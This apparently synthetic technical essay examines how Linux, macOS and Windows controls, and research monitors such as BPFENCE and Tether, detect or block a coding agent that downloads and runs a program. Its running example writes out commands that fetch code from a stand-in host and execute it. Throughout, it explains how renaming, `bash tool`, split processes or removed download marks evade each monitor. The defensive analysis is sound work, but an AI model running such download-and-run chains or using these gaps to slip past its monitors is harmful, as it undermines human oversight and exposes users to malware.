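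Other ways of running downloaded code leave different traces. Running `bash tool` produces an exec event for Bash, and `tool` appears only as a file that Bash opens for reading. Piping a download into a shell produces exec events for curl and Bash but none for a new file.

The events also don't show where a file's contents came from. Curl connects to the network and writes the file in separate requests to the operating system, so a monitor has to infer that the bytes written are the bytes downloaded. That is a safe guess for curl but a poor one for a code editor or the agent's own program, which may stay connected to the network all day and also save files that the user wrote.

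### Hooks that block and hooks that report

Many Linux monitors collect events with eBPF, which runs small programs inside the kernel. Elastic, for example, uses it on newer kernels to record process starts and new files. The kernel's verifier checks each eBPF program before it runs and rejects any that might loop forever or access memory it shouldn't. This stops a faulty monitor from crashing the machine, but it also limits what the monitor can compute. The programs can store data in maps, which are tables in kernel memory that persist between events and that several programs can share.

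An eBPF program is attached to a hook, a point in the kernel's work, and runs when the kernel reaches it. Galletta (2026), in *Enforcement of In-Kernel Stateful Security Policies via eBPF*, distinguishes hooks by whether they can stop an event. Linux Security Module hooks run before a sensitive operation finishes, and the kernel refuses the operation if the eBPF program returns an error. Tracepoints and kprobes, two other kinds of hook, can only report events.

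If a blocking hook refuses to execute `./tool`, none of the file's code runs. A tracepoint reports the program only after it has started, and a program can read an access key and send it away in a fraction of a second.

### Published rules for newly written programs

Falco is an open-source monitor for Linux machines and containers. A container is an isolated environment that starts from a fixed image, a package of files that someone prepared in advance. Falco's rule "Drop and execute new binary in container" raises an alert when a container starts a program that wasn't in its image. According to Douglas (2024), in *Container Drift Detection with Falco*, the rule has four conditions:

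- a new process has started;
- it is running in a container;
- its program file is in the upper layer of the container's file system;
- the container's image is not on a list of exceptions.

Overlayfs, a common file system for containers, keeps everything written since the container started in an upper layer, separate from older files. Falco can therefore identify new files without a record of the download. This works only in containers that use overlayfs.

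In a container with this file system, the rule would flag `./tool`. It would also flag a program an agent has just compiled from the user's source, since that file is new too. It would miss `bash tool`, because the running program is Bash, which came with the image.

According to Falco, administrators who debug a live container are a common source of false alarms. Falco's advice is to list images known to run new programs, or to exclude systems that aren't in production. That advice suits web servers, which should never change after launch. A coding agent works in a development environment, where new programs appear all day, so following it could exclude the containers in which agents run.

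Falco also has rules for the other two steps, but they are noisy. One reports curl and similar tools starting in a container. Another reports any chmod that sets an execute bit, and Douglas says that Falco disables it by default because of the noise. Falco's *Default Rules* confirms that a standard installation loads only the rules the project considers stable. These include the rule for new programs but not the one for curl. They also include one for programs that run from memory without ever being on disk.

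All of these rules judge single events. Elastic's *File Creation, Execution and Self-Deletion in Suspicious Directory* (2023) looks for a sequence on one machine and under one user account, within one minute:

| Event | Conditions |
|---|---|
| A file appears | curl, wget or one of seven other programs created it in a directory such as `/tmp` |
| A program starts | It is in one of those directories and has the same name as the file |
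| A file with that name disappears | The program that deleted it is not `rm` or one of five build tools |

This rule comes close to matching the fetch-chmod-execute chain, but the running example wouldn't trigger it because the agent saved `tool` in the project folder and nothing deleted the file afterwards. Removing the deletion step and adding the project folder would make the rule match, but it would then also match every tool that a developer downloads and runs within a minute.

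Elastic warns that even with the deletion step, the rule can raise false alarms on tests, updates, and installers that fetch a helper program, run it, and clean up. The seven other programs include `ld`, which writes the finished program when a C compiler runs, so a test suite that compiles a small program in `/tmp`, runs it, and deletes it could set off the rule.

Elastic gives this sequence a risk score of 73 out of 100. Its rule *File Made Executable via Chmod Inside A Container* (2025), which covers only the chmod step, has a score of 21. The sequence rule searches stored logs, so its alert comes too late to stop the program from starting.

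Another approach looks only at where a program is stored. *Potentially Suspicious Execution From Tmp Folder* (Sanchez, 2023) does this with a rule in Sigma, an open format that many monitoring products can read. The rule does not cover programs saved in the project folder.

Elastic's *Curl or Wget Egress Network Connection via LoLBin* does cover the full chain in its advice to analysts, which is to escalate an alert if someone made a downloaded program executable and then ran it. The analyst connects these steps after they have happened. The same page recommends mounting `/tmp` and similar directories with the option `noexec`, which stops the kernel from starting programs there. This requires no detection, but few developers could apply it to a project folder where they also compile and run their own code.

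Blocking is rare. Douglas cites a report by the security company Sysdig in which about 25% of users of Kubernetes, a system for managing containers, received alerts about changed containers, and about 4% of teams blocked unexpected programs automatically.

### A monitor that remembers and blocks

Galletta's system, BPFENCE, can block an event inside the kernel based on the events that came before it. His main example is an intruder who takes three steps that are each normal on their own: reading a private key for SSH (a program for logging in to other machines), connecting to another machine, and running a command there.

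The policy for this attack defines two history predicates, which are statements that start out false and stay true once an event has made them true. `key_read` becomes true when a process opens a private key. `ssh_connected` becomes true when the process connects to port 22, the usual port for SSH, but only if `key_read` is already true. A forbid-when rule then prohibits the process from starting any program while `ssh_connected` is true. In the notation used earlier for the file rule, with the diamond now including the present moment, the policy is:

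□ ¬[ ◆(◆key_read ∧ connect) ∧ exec ]

BPFENCE checks that the kernel can enforce a policy before accepting it. If a policy denies an event at a hook that can only report it, the compiler rejects the policy. The standard library covers 14 types of event, 13 of which use blocking hooks.

The compiler then builds a monitor. Each forbid rule becomes a machine with two states, "ok" and "violated", and each history predicate becomes one bit of memory. When an event arrives, the monitor first updates the bits and then checks the rules. The compiler writes one eBPF program for each hook that the policy needs, and these programs share the bits through a map. The number of rules is fixed in advance, so the generated code needs no loops and can pass the verifier.

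Galletta proves that the monitor reports a violation only if the sequence of events breaks the policy, and that it detects every violation if it receives every relevant event. For rules with deadlines, some event must also arrive after the deadline. The proofs cover only the abstract monitor, so users still have to trust the kernel and the compiler that turns the monitor into eBPF code.

Galletta describes the first result as "no false positives", meaning that the monitor stops only programs that break the policy. Those programs may still be harmless. A policy that forbade all programs, for example, would stop every harmless one without producing a false positive in this sense. Experiments are needed to determine whether a policy separates attacks from normal work.

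### Seven case studies and a web server

Galletta tested BPFENCE on seven policies. For each one he ran a program that imitated an attack and another that did something similar but legitimate.

| Policy | Behaviour it targets | Response |
|---|---|---|
| Server sandbox | A server starts a shell, which then runs programs, opens connections or changes settings | Kill |
| Resource exhaustion | A process copies itself, or opens connections, at an extreme rate | Alert |
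| Container isolation | Secret data moves to a less trusted container | Deny |
| Data theft | A process reads a sensitive file, then opens a connection | Deny |
| SSH attack | The three steps described above | Kill |
| Persistence | After starting a shell, a process changes the password file or scheduled tasks | Kill |
| File integrity | An unauthorised program writes to a protected file | Deny |

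BPFENCE responded as intended to all seven attacks and did not interfere with any of the seven legitimate programs. None of the attacks is the fetch-chmod-execute chain. The data theft policy covers almost the reverse sequence, in which file access comes before network access.

Testing one harmless program per policy also provides very little evidence about false alarms. Even if the seven programs were a random sample of normal activity, which they aren't, zero alarms would be compatible with a false-positive rate of up to about 35%.

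The effect on speed is better documented. With two of the policies loaded, the web server nginx handled 147,223 requests per second instead of 155,798, a drop of 5.5%. In a test that only opened and closed files, a one-rule policy added 240 nanoseconds to an operation that normally took 1,318, or about 18%. Most of the extra time went into working out the file's full path. Compiling a large project or installing packages can open thousands of files, so a coding agent could slow down more than nginx did, but Galletta didn't measure such work.

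BPFENCE's threat model also assumes that the attacker can run any code in a monitored process but does not actively try to evade known policies, for example by splitting an attack across several processes. As partial protection against such splitting, Galletta has made each new process inherit the history of the process that started it. He leaves attacks by cooperating processes to future work.

### A policy for the chain

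The following policy is an illustration in BPFENCE's language and does not come from Galletta's paper. The project is in the folder `/work`.

```
import stdlib linux files
import stdlib linux network
import stdlib linux process

let connected = happened(connect(_, _))

let fetched = happened(write("/work/*")) when connected

policy download_then_run {
    apply to pid action deny
    forbid exec("/work/*") when fetched
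}
```

`connected` becomes true after any network connection, and `fetched` becomes true after a later write to a file in `/work`. From then on, the policy blocks programs in that folder from starting. It doesn't check for chmod because some downloaded code runs without it. BPFENCE also can't yet test individual bits in a system call's arguments, so a chmod condition would probably have to list whole permission values such as 755.

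The line `apply to pid` gives each process its own history. Tracing the running example by hand shows that this version fails. The shell starts curl in one process and `./tool` in another. Curl's process connects and writes, so its `fetched` becomes true. But history passes only from parent to child, and the parent of `./tool` is the shell, which has neither connected nor written anything. BPFENCE would therefore let `./tool` start.

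An attacker doesn't have to split the attack to cause this, because the shell does so in normal use. The same version would detect an installer that downloads a program into `/work` and starts it itself, because the new process would inherit the installer's history.

Replacing `pid` with `cgroup` gives all processes in a container one shared history. (Containers use cgroups, the kernel's way of grouping processes.) The table traces both versions through the seven-command session from the earlier comparison, followed by a second run of the user's own program. It assumes that the agent's main program runs outside the container and only its commands run inside.

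| Command | `fetched` in the container | History per process | History per container |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1. `cc -o app app.c` | False | Allow | Allow |
| 2. `./app` | False | Allow | Allow |
| 3. `curl -o tool example.org/tool` | True | Allow | Allow |
| 4. `chmod +x tool` | True | Allow | Allow |
| 5. `./tool` | True | Allow | Refuse |
| 6. `curl -o setup.sh example.org/setup.sh` | True | Allow | Allow |
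| 7. `bash setup.sh` | True | Allow | Allow |
| 8. `./app` | True | Allow | Refuse |

With a shared history, the policy stops the downloaded program at step 5, but it also blocks the user's own program at step 8, which it allowed at step 2. BPFENCE never resets a history predicate while the container exists, so no program in `/work` can start after the first download. Step 7 passes in both versions because the exec event lists Bash as the program, so it would pass even if nobody had reviewed the script.

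The table follows the generated code, which checks each event afresh. In the formal model, a monitor stays in the "violated" state once it reaches it, so it would refuse every event it handles after step 5.

The result would be worse if the agent's main program ran inside the container. The program connects to the model's server before doing anything else, so the first source file it saved would set `fetched` to true. The policy would then block `./app` at step 2, before the agent had downloaded anything.

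### Requiring the same file

The false alarm at step 8 arises because the policy connects a write to one file with the start of another. The file-state rule described earlier avoids this by keeping a separate record for each file. In BPFENCE's language, a similar rule might look like this, where `?X` stores the file's identity and `X` requires the same one:

```
let fetched = happened(write(file = ?X))
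forbid exec(file = X) when fetched
```

BPFENCE's definition doesn't allow this. The language has variables of this kind, and Galletta uses them in a rule that every open file must be closed within five seconds. But under the definition in the appendix, a history predicate may neither set nor use a variable. Each predicate is a single yes or no for the whole process or container, so it doesn't record which file made it true.

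The language's other constructs don't solve the problem. A deadline rule can refer to the same file twice, but it raises an alarm when the later event doesn't happen, so it would flag downloads that nobody ran. The sequence construct works the same way because BPFENCE translates it into deadlines. Rules with deadlines also can't block actions, only raise alerts.

Another construct, bounded safety, forbids an event if a different one has happened within a set time. Galletta's example is a ban on contacting a destination again within ten seconds, which seems to require remembering the destination. However, he describes a counter stored per rule and per process or container, with no field for a destination or a file. With a ten-minute limit, `./app` could run again ten minutes after the last write, but so could `tool`.

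A policy can connect the two events if it gives the exact path, such as `/work/tool`, in both places. With a shared history, it would block `./tool` and allow `./app`. BPFENCE identifies a file listed by exact path by more than the path itself, so renaming the file wouldn't help an attacker. But whoever writes the policy would have to know the download's name in advance.

Approvals have the same limitation. The file integrity policy in the case studies allows a write only if an authorised program has run, and a similar rule could require a scanner to run before any program in `/work` starts. But once the scanner had examined one file, the predicate would stay true and every other file would pass too.

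Elastic's sequence rule requires the file and the program to have the same name, but it can't block anything. BPFENCE can block, but it can't link a file to the program unless it knows about the file in advance. Adding that link would be a fairly small change, because the deadline rules already store file identities in a map. Galletta also plans to extend BPFENCE to track how data moves between processes.

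### Telling the agent from the user

The agent normally works under the developer's account, so the user ID in a monitor's events doesn't show which of them downloaded a file or ran it. Elastic's sequence rule groups events by machine and user, so it would combine a file that the agent downloaded with a program of the same name that the developer started.

The chain of parent processes is better evidence of whether an agent or a person ran a command, because an agent's command usually descends from the agent's program and a person's from a terminal. Elastic's rule *Curl or Wget Spawned via Node.js* uses this kind of evidence to flag downloads started by the JavaScript runtime Node.js, which it rates as low severity. Some coding agents run on Node.js, so their routine downloads could trigger the rule.

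A process's parentage can also be misleading. A code editor can start both the user's terminal and the agent's shell, so the two share an ancestor. A program that keeps running after its parent exits gets a new parent. A scheduled task doesn't descend from the agent, even if the agent created it.

Some rules use the presence of a terminal as a sign that a person is running the commands. Elastic's *File Download Detected via Defend for Containers*, for example, applies only to interactive sessions. That is reasonable for catching an intruder who types commands, but agents often run commands without a terminal, and the rule would miss downloads made that way.

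Giving the agent its own container or user account is a more reliable way to tell its commands from the developer's, since every event then carries an identifier that the developer's commands don't have. A log of tool calls can also link events to the requests that led to them. Neither shows whether the user wanted the software, which depends on the conversation rather than on kernel events.

Keeping separate histories for the container and the terminal also creates a gap if the agent and the user share the project folder. The agent may download `tool` in its container, and the user may later run it from an ordinary terminal. The monitor then records the download in one history and the run in another, so it doesn't flag the sequence.

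## Tracking where a file came from and refusing to run it

An origin label attaches the record of a download to the file instead of the container, so a monitor could still recognise `tool` when the user ran it from a terminal. The label marks the file's contents as trusted or untrusted, and every copy gets the same mark, whatever its name.

### How a label follows a file

Suppose the agent copies `tool` and renames the copy before running it, perhaps because the project's setup notes call for a different name.

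| Command | Event | Files labelled untrusted afterwards |
|---|---|---|
| `curl -o tool example.org/tool` | Contents arrive from an untrusted server | `tool` |
| `cp tool helper` | Copy | `tool`, `helper` |
| `mv helper fmt` | Rename | `tool`, `fmt` |
| `chmod +x fmt` | Permission change | `tool`, `fmt` |
| `./fmt` | Start | `tool`, `fmt` |

To judge `./fmt`, a check only has to look up the label of `fmt`. A rule that searches a log of past events has to reconstruct the copying first. Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues (2026), in *Tether*, work out how quickly such rules multiply. If the log distinguishes *m* kinds of copying, a chain of *j* copies can take *m*ʲ forms, so covering every chain of up to *k* copies takes this many patterns:

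*m* + *m*² + … + *m*ᵏ

If each step can change a file in one of three ways (say copying, renaming or unpacking), covering every sequence of one to four steps takes 3 + 9 + 27 + 81 = 120 patterns, and a fifth step evades them all. Using labels that track a file's origin takes only one rule, regardless of the number of steps.

Files unpacked from an untrusted archive are untrusted too. When a program combines several files, the result is untrusted if any of them was. A program compiled from downloaded source code is therefore untrusted, whereas the file-state rule described earlier treated every local build as the user's own.

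But most projects contain libraries that a package manager downloaded. If these are all untrusted, so is every program built from them, and a rule against running untrusted files would stop the agent from testing its own work. Labelling the main package collections as trusted would fix this, but any malicious packages they carry, such as function-color on npm, would then be trusted too.

Labels also need protection from tampering. macOS and Windows store theirs with the file, where any program can find them, but a program running under the user's account may be able to delete them. A monitor can instead keep the labels in a table that the agent can't reach, but then it protects only commands that pass through the monitor, which may not include those run in the user's own terminal. Such protection seems to be rare. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) reviewed 71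 works related to recording what agents do and found little reporting of records that reveal tampering.

### Running a command before deciding on it

Researchers at Google DeepMind, Google and two American universities published the Tether monitor in November 2026. It keeps labels in its own table and updates them from system calls, so it also tracks files that a script moves.

Tether runs each command, then decides whether to keep the results. The command runs in a temporary layer on top of the real file system, built with overlayfs, which Falco also uses to spot new files in containers. The command can read the machine's files, but its changes go into the temporary layer. The tracing program strace records the command's system calls, and a local proxy holds its network requests.

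Tether then translates the recorded calls into 11 abstract actions.

| What happens | Abstract actions |
|---|---|
| The agent learns something | `read`, `recvNet` |
| A file changes | `write`, `create`, `delete` |
| Contents move into a file | `copy`, `concatenate`, `downloadNet` |
| Data leaves the machine | `sendNet`, `uploadNet` |
| The agent gains administrator rights | `escalatePrivilege` |

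A policy allows or denies each action. When the command makes a network request, Tether checks all the command's actions up to that point, then forwards or drops the request. When the command ends, Tether copies the command's changes to the real file system if the policy allowed every action, and otherwise discards them.

In Sistla and colleagues' example, an agent uploads a status report to GitHub, copies a confidential inventory over the report, and uploads the report again with the same command. Tether allows the first upload and blocks the second, because the copy gave the report the inventory's label. A check that looks at one command at a time couldn't tell the two uploads apart, just as it can't judge `./tool`, because the command doesn't show where the file's contents came from.

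If a program reads one file and then writes another, Tether assumes that data from the first went into the second. This assumption is often wrong, and when it is, Tether keeps a label it should have dropped.

### The label of a download

Each of Tether's labels has two parts. The confidentiality part is Public, Internal, Sensitive or Secret, and the integrity part is Trusted or Untrusted. To combine two labels, Tether takes the more restrictive value of each part, an operation written ⊔. When a command downloads something from server *s* to file *d*, the file's new label is

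σ(*d*) = σ(*s*) ⊔ loc(*d*)

Here σ is the label on the file's contents, and loc(*d*) is the location label of the folder that holds it. Suppose someone has labelled example.org (Public, Untrusted) and the project folder (Public, Trusted). After the curl command, `tool` is (Public, Untrusted).

The formula for a copy is the same, with the original file in place of the server. Tether treats a rename as a copy followed by a deletion, and the deletion resets the label on the old name. It treats `chmod` as a write to the file's permissions, so the label on the contents doesn't change. Tether would therefore produce the labels in the table above without any rules specific to `cp` or `mv`.

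The agent's context, meaning everything it has read so far, also has a label. If the agent prints a downloaded script and retypes it into a new file, the new file inherits the Untrusted label from the context. So does every other file the agent writes after that, including files unrelated to the script. A download that goes straight to disk doesn't affect the context, so saving a file with curl doesn't by itself make the agent's later files Untrusted.

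Sistla and colleagues wrote the policy language in Lean, a system for machine-checked proofs, and proved seven guarantees about the policy they tested. One is that no Secret data enters the agent's context if none was there at the start. The proofs cover abstract actions, so the guarantees hold on a real machine only if Tether translates system calls into those actions correctly.

To look for translation errors, the team generated random sequences of file operations, carried them out in different ways, such as through pipes, links and direct transfers inside the kernel, and compared Tether's verdicts and labels with the correct ones. They also had a Gemini 3.8 Flash agent try to get around the monitor in ten tasks. The agent's success rate fell from 40% to 0% over three versions of Tether. One of the gaps they closed involved hard links, which give a file a second name without copying it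 and so would have let the file lose its label.

### What the tests cover

In their main tests, Sistla and colleagues replayed recorded agent sessions from two benchmarks. MonitoringBenchHonest has system administration tasks in 88 containers, and LinuxArena has software work in ten imitation production environments. In the attack runs, the agent also pursued a harmful side task. They compared Tether with an open-source version of Claude Code's auto mode running on Claude Sonnet 5, once with its default rules and once with Tether's policy added to its instructions.

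| Monitor | MonitoringBenchHonest: 199 attacks blocked | 218 harmless runs blocked | LinuxArena: 145 attacks blocked | 1,372 harmless runs blocked |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Tether | 100% | 2.3% | 100% | 5.0% |
| Auto mode, default rules | 86.9% | 35.3% | 97.9% | 5.7% |
| Auto mode, with Tether's policy | 82.4% | 14.7% | 98.6% | 1.7% |

Tether clearly did better on the first benchmark. On the second, auto mode with the policy missed two attacks but raised only a third as many false alarms. Auto mode judged scripts from the command line, so it didn't detect attacks hidden inside them. Tracing system calls is most useful for those attacks.

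Tether raised 74 false alarms. Fifty came from edits to protected files such as `/etc/passwd` that the task hadn't asked for, and package installers made some of those edits. Another 17 came from commands such as a recursive text search, which opens every file it reaches, including secret ones. The remaining seven involved servers that the task hadn't declared.

These rates are per run, whereas the rates for CARE were per command. If, hypothetically, one run in a thousand were an attack, Tether would still raise more than 45 false alarms for every correct one. Sistla and colleagues also used benchmark runs to refine the policy, so both the detection rate and the false-positive rate could be worse on new tasks.

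The 100% applies only to runs in which Tether could trace and model every action. Sistla and colleagues excluded runs that needed outside services they couldn't imitate and runs they couldn't replay to the end, and they don't give a number for either. For the rest they give percentages instead of counts:

| Reason a run was out of scope | MonitoringBenchHonest | LinuxArena |
|---|---|---|
| Judging it requires understanding the content | 28.2% | 22.1% |
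| It uses background processes or databases | 36.3% | 71.5% |

An agent that writes a deliberate flaw into a file it is allowed to edit belongs in the first row. No rule about the flow of data can catch that. Tether can't follow the data in detail for actions in the second row, but a stricter policy can refuse them altogether. Under that policy, a coding agent couldn't start a web server in the background to test a page.

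It is unclear from the paper whether these are percentages of all replayable runs or only of those outside the main test, so they can't be converted to counts. If they are percentages of all replayable runs, the main test covered at most about 36% of those runs on MonitoringBenchHonest and 6% on LinuxArena.

### When the downloaded program starts

None of Tether's 11 abstract actions is "run a program". Tether monitors the system call that starts a program to work out which process started which, but it turns that call into an abstract action only for sudo and similar programs that change the user's privileges. A policy therefore can't forbid starting any other program, because the event never reaches it.

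Four of the full policy's 24 rules apply to downloads. They refuse a download if it would overwrite a sensitive file, would land in a protected system folder, comes from a blocked server, or comes from a server the task hasn't declared. Unless someone narrows it for a task, the list of declared servers is a single wildcard that matches every address. Anything without its own label gets (Public, Trusted) by default. So under the default settings, `tool` arrives from example.org labelled as trusted.

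Labelling example.org as untrusted changes little. The policy lets untrusted contents into any file that isn't Sensitive or Secret, so the download still succeeds. The policy also allows `chmod` on a file in the project folder, and `./tool` then starts without a check. Even `sudo ./tool` would pass if the agent hadn't read anything untrusted or sensitive beforehand, because the rule on administrator rights checks the label of the agent's context, not the program's.

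Tether does restrict what the program can do next. If `tool` tries to read the user's saved Amazon Web Services credentials, which the policy labels Secret, Tether blocks it and discards everything the command changed. Tether also stops the program from editing protected system files or uploading Sensitive data to outside servers. But the program can rewrite the project's source code, and with the default list of servers it can also send that code anywhere, because ordinary files are Public.

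The label can also get lost when a downloaded program runs. Tether adds a file to a program's sources when the program reads the file with a system call, but the kernel loads the program's own code without such a read. As far as the published definitions show, a downloaded installer that contains a second program could therefore write that program to disk with a clean label.

The test results are therefore evidence that Tether limits the damage a program can do, wherever it came from, but not direct evidence about the fetch-chmod-execute chain. Sistla and colleagues mention downloading and running malicious programs as a risk, but they don't report how many of the 344 attacks did this, and none of their seven guarantees covers which programs may start.

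The missing piece looks small. With a twelfth action, here called `execute`, a rule in Tether's language could read as follows. (This is an illustration and not part of the paper.)

```
rule restrict_untrusted_start : on execute(src)
  if σ[src, content].I ⊑ Trusted
  then allow else deny "untrusted program"
```

The condition is true only if the integrity part of the file's label is Trusted. Outside servers would need Untrusted as their default label, and Tether would have to emit `execute` when an interpreter reads a script as well as when the kernel starts a program. There would also have to be a way to approve files. The standard action for this is endorsing, which Sistla and colleagues left out because their policy didn't need it, though they say it is easy to add. Endorsing only files whose hashes are on an approved list would give the same protection as the file-state rule, and it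 would work inside scripts too.

Tether reads encrypted web traffic only for the imitation servers in the tests, but most real downloads are encrypted. Strace also slowed the experiments considerably, though the team expects a faster tracer, such as one based on eBPF, could replace it.

### Marks on downloaded files in macOS and Windows

Several older controls act on the last step without tracing anything. The comparison below shows how they and the two versions of Tether would handle the downloaded program, a program the user has just compiled, and a downloaded shell script passed to Bash.

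| Control | `./tool` | `./app` | `bash tool` |
|---|---|---|---|
| macOS quarantine flag | Allowed unless known malware | Allowed | Allowed |
| fapolicyd, default rules | Refused | Refused | Allowed |
| Project folder mounted with `noexec` | Refused | Refused | Allowed |
| Tether, published policy | Allowed, effects checked | Allowed, effects checked | Allowed, effects checked |
| Tether with the rule above | Refused | Allowed | Refused |

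On a Mac, a browser attaches a quarantine flag to the files it downloads. According to MITRE ATT&CK's *Subvert Trust Controls*, the flag triggers Gatekeeper, the part of macOS that checks new software. Gatekeeper asks the user for permission and checks that a registered developer has signed the program and that Apple has notarized it, which means that Apple has scanned it for known malware. The Eclectic Light Company's *What is Gatekeeper, and where can I see it?* (2019) explains that the flag usually survives unpacking because most programs that open archives pass it on to the extracted files.

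The weakness is that the downloading program has to set the flag. MITRE ATT&CK notes that curl may not, and lists CoinTicker, Mac malware that used curl to download a component that wasn't flagged. Other malware on the list deletes the flag with a single command. An agent could run the same command without bad intent, because it is a quick way to get a blocked program to start.

Gatekeeper has a second check that doesn't need the flag. Apple's *Gatekeeper and runtime protection in macOS* says that macOS checks all software for known malicious content the first time it's opened, however it arrived. Since the 2019 version, this has included programs started from a command line, according to WWDC Notes' *Advances in macOS Security*. Malware that isn't yet known would pass this check. Apple also says that Gatekeeper records where files written by downloaded software came from, a link that Tether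 seems to lose, but it doesn't say that this record alone can stop a program.

Windows has a similar mark, the Mark of the Web, in a hidden data stream attached to the file. SmartScreen, Microsoft's check on downloads, checks marked programs, and Office opens marked documents in a restricted view. The copy of curl that comes with Windows 11 doesn't write the mark, according to a 2016 post, since updated, on the web security blog text/plain. Copying a file to a USB stick with an older file system removes the mark. Files unpacked from a marked archive may not inherit it, according to the Center for Threat-Informed Defense's *T1553.005 Mark-of-the-Web Bypass Mappings*.

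A program that saves a file before marking it also leaves a short interval in which something else can open the file unmarked, as text/plain's *Mark-of-the-Web* (2022) warns. An agent's next command might open the file in that interval, though a person rarely would.

Both marks were designed for people who download files in a browser and double-click them. They would probably have helped somewhat against a web page like Rehberger's, where the agent downloaded the program with Firefox, but they do almost nothing about files downloaded with curl.

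### Lists of approved programs

An approved-program list instead treats every file as untrusted until someone lists it. On Linux, the fapolicyd service enforces such a list. Whenever a program starts or opens a file, the kernel waits for fapolicyd to allow or deny the action.

By default the list contains the software that the system's package manager has installed. Red Hat's *Blocking and allowing applications by using fapolicyd* demonstrates the effect by copying `ls`, the standard program for listing files, to `/tmp`. The copy won't run, even though its contents are identical. A copy of a trusted file has to be added to the list separately, so the monitor doesn't have to catch every copy. With origin labels it does, because each copy of an untrusted file has to be labeled too.

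Fapolicyd would therefore refuse `./tool` without any record of the download. It would also refuse a compiled program downloaded through a browser or extracted from an archive. But it would refuse `./app` too, since no package manager installed it. The user can add `app` to the list, but has to update the entry whenever the agent recompiles it and the contents change. A rule that allows everything in the project folder would prevent these refusals, but it would also allow `./tool`.

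By default, the service doesn't check whether a listed file's contents have changed. An administrator has to turn on checking by either file size or SHA-256 hash. Hashes are slower but safer, since Red Hat warns that an attacker can replace a file with another of the same size. Without hash checking, an entry for `app` in the project folder could end up covering whatever program the agent later saved under that name.

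Scripts leave a larger gap. Oracle's *Managing Policies* lists a typical set of rules, in which the first rule that matches a file applies. Rule 11 blocks unlisted files in Python, Perl, JavaScript and many other languages. Rule 12 allows every shell script, so `python3 tool.py` fails but `bash tool` works. On a developer's machine, rule 11 would also block the user's own Python project.

The exception for shell scripts is deliberate. fapolicyd's *File Access Policy Daemon* argues that running a script is not much different from typing its commands by hand, and that fapolicyd still checks each program the script calls. This is reasonable if the worry is that a script will bring in new software. But a stranger chose the commands in a downloaded script, and they can do plenty of harm with approved programs, such as deleting the project with `rm` or sending a private key away with `curl`.

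An interpreter may also read a script piece by piece while running it. Debian's *fapolicyd.rules* points out that anyone with write permission can add to the file after the check.

### Folders where nothing can start

The `noexec` mount option, which Elastic recommends for temporary directories, blocks programs without needing a list, and `chmod +x` doesn't override it. The obvious setup applies `noexec` to a separate download folder but not to the project folder, so an agent that gets "Permission denied" can copy the file to the project folder and try again.

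The option also has the same hole as fapolicyd: `bash tool` still works, because Bash is stored elsewhere.

According to the Linux kernel documentation's *Executability check* (2024), an interpreter on Linux can now check with the kernel whether a script would be allowed to start directly, and refuse to run it if not. Then `bash tool` and `./tool` have the same result. This works only with interpreters whose developers have added the check, and only if the administrator has turned on enforcement, which is off by default.

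In an ordinary folder, an agent could still pass the check by running `chmod +x` first. But the check would at least force the agent to run chmod before running a script, which would help a detector that looks for that step.

A second setting covers code that doesn't come from a file, such as a download piped into a shell. Interpreters that follow it must also refuse commands passed to them as an argument. Agents usually pass commands to the shell this way, so turning the setting on for the agent's own shell would disable the shell tool.

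### Signatures and checksums

A checksum would have exposed the altered Codecov script to any customer who had saved one for the original. With digital signatures, the publisher signs each new version with a private key, and anyone can verify the signature with the matching public key. An attacker who breaks into the download server might be able to change the listed checksums, but can't produce a valid signature without the private key.

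Neither shows whether the publisher is honest. The attacker who registered the package name in Clerk's documentation could have signed the malware as the package's rightful owner. Scanning before signing helps only with malware that the scanner can already recognize. MITRE ATT&CK records that Apple notarized a version of Shlayer, the Mac malware that uses curl and chmod. Apple can revoke a program's approval later, and Macs check for revocations often, but this protects only users who haven't run the program yet.

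A signature also helps only if something checks it before the file runs. If the system verifies programs as they start, running `bash tool` makes it verify Bash but not the script `tool`.

### Sandboxes and network limits

Each of these controls can be bypassed, so what a running program can access also matters. Cursor documents the following defaults for the sandbox where its agent runs commands.

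| Resource | Default access |
|---|---|
| Files in the project | Read and write |
| Temporary directories | Full |
| Other files on the machine | Read only |
| Cursor's own configuration folder | Protected from changes |
| Network | Blocked, or limited to a list of addresses when enabled |

The running example fails at the first command because example.org isn't on Cursor's list, so no detector is needed. But the list includes GitHub's file hosting. If the attacker publishes `tool` there and network access is on, the agent can download it, make it executable and run it inside the sandbox without a prompt.

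The program then can't change files outside the project and temporary directories, so it can't add itself to the user's startup programs. It also can't connect to the attacker's server, and that restriction would have cut Rehberger off from the machine. It can't loosen the sandbox by editing Cursor's settings either.

The downloaded program can still read the user's other files, including any private keys, but it can send them only to addresses on the allowed list. Cursor's default list includes several cloud storage services where anyone can open an account, and a limit on addresses doesn't distinguish the attacker's account from the developer's. Cursor also has a stricter setting that permits only addresses the user has listed. If a project's packages are already installed, that list can be empty, which blocks both the download and any attempt to send the user's files out.

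Users can lift these limits. When a sandboxed command fails, Cursor lets the user skip it, run it without the sandbox, or add it to the allowlist. An agent's failed attempt to reach example.org will therefore often lead to a prompt that the user can answer in a second. On Linux machines with a kernel older than 6.2, the sandbox isn't available, and Cursor asks for approval instead.

Whatever the program writes to the project also stays there after the program ends. It could add a line to the build script, and that line would run outside the sandbox the next time the developer builds the project from an ordinary terminal. Reviewing the git changes before each build would reveal an edited script, but not a new program in a folder that git ignores.
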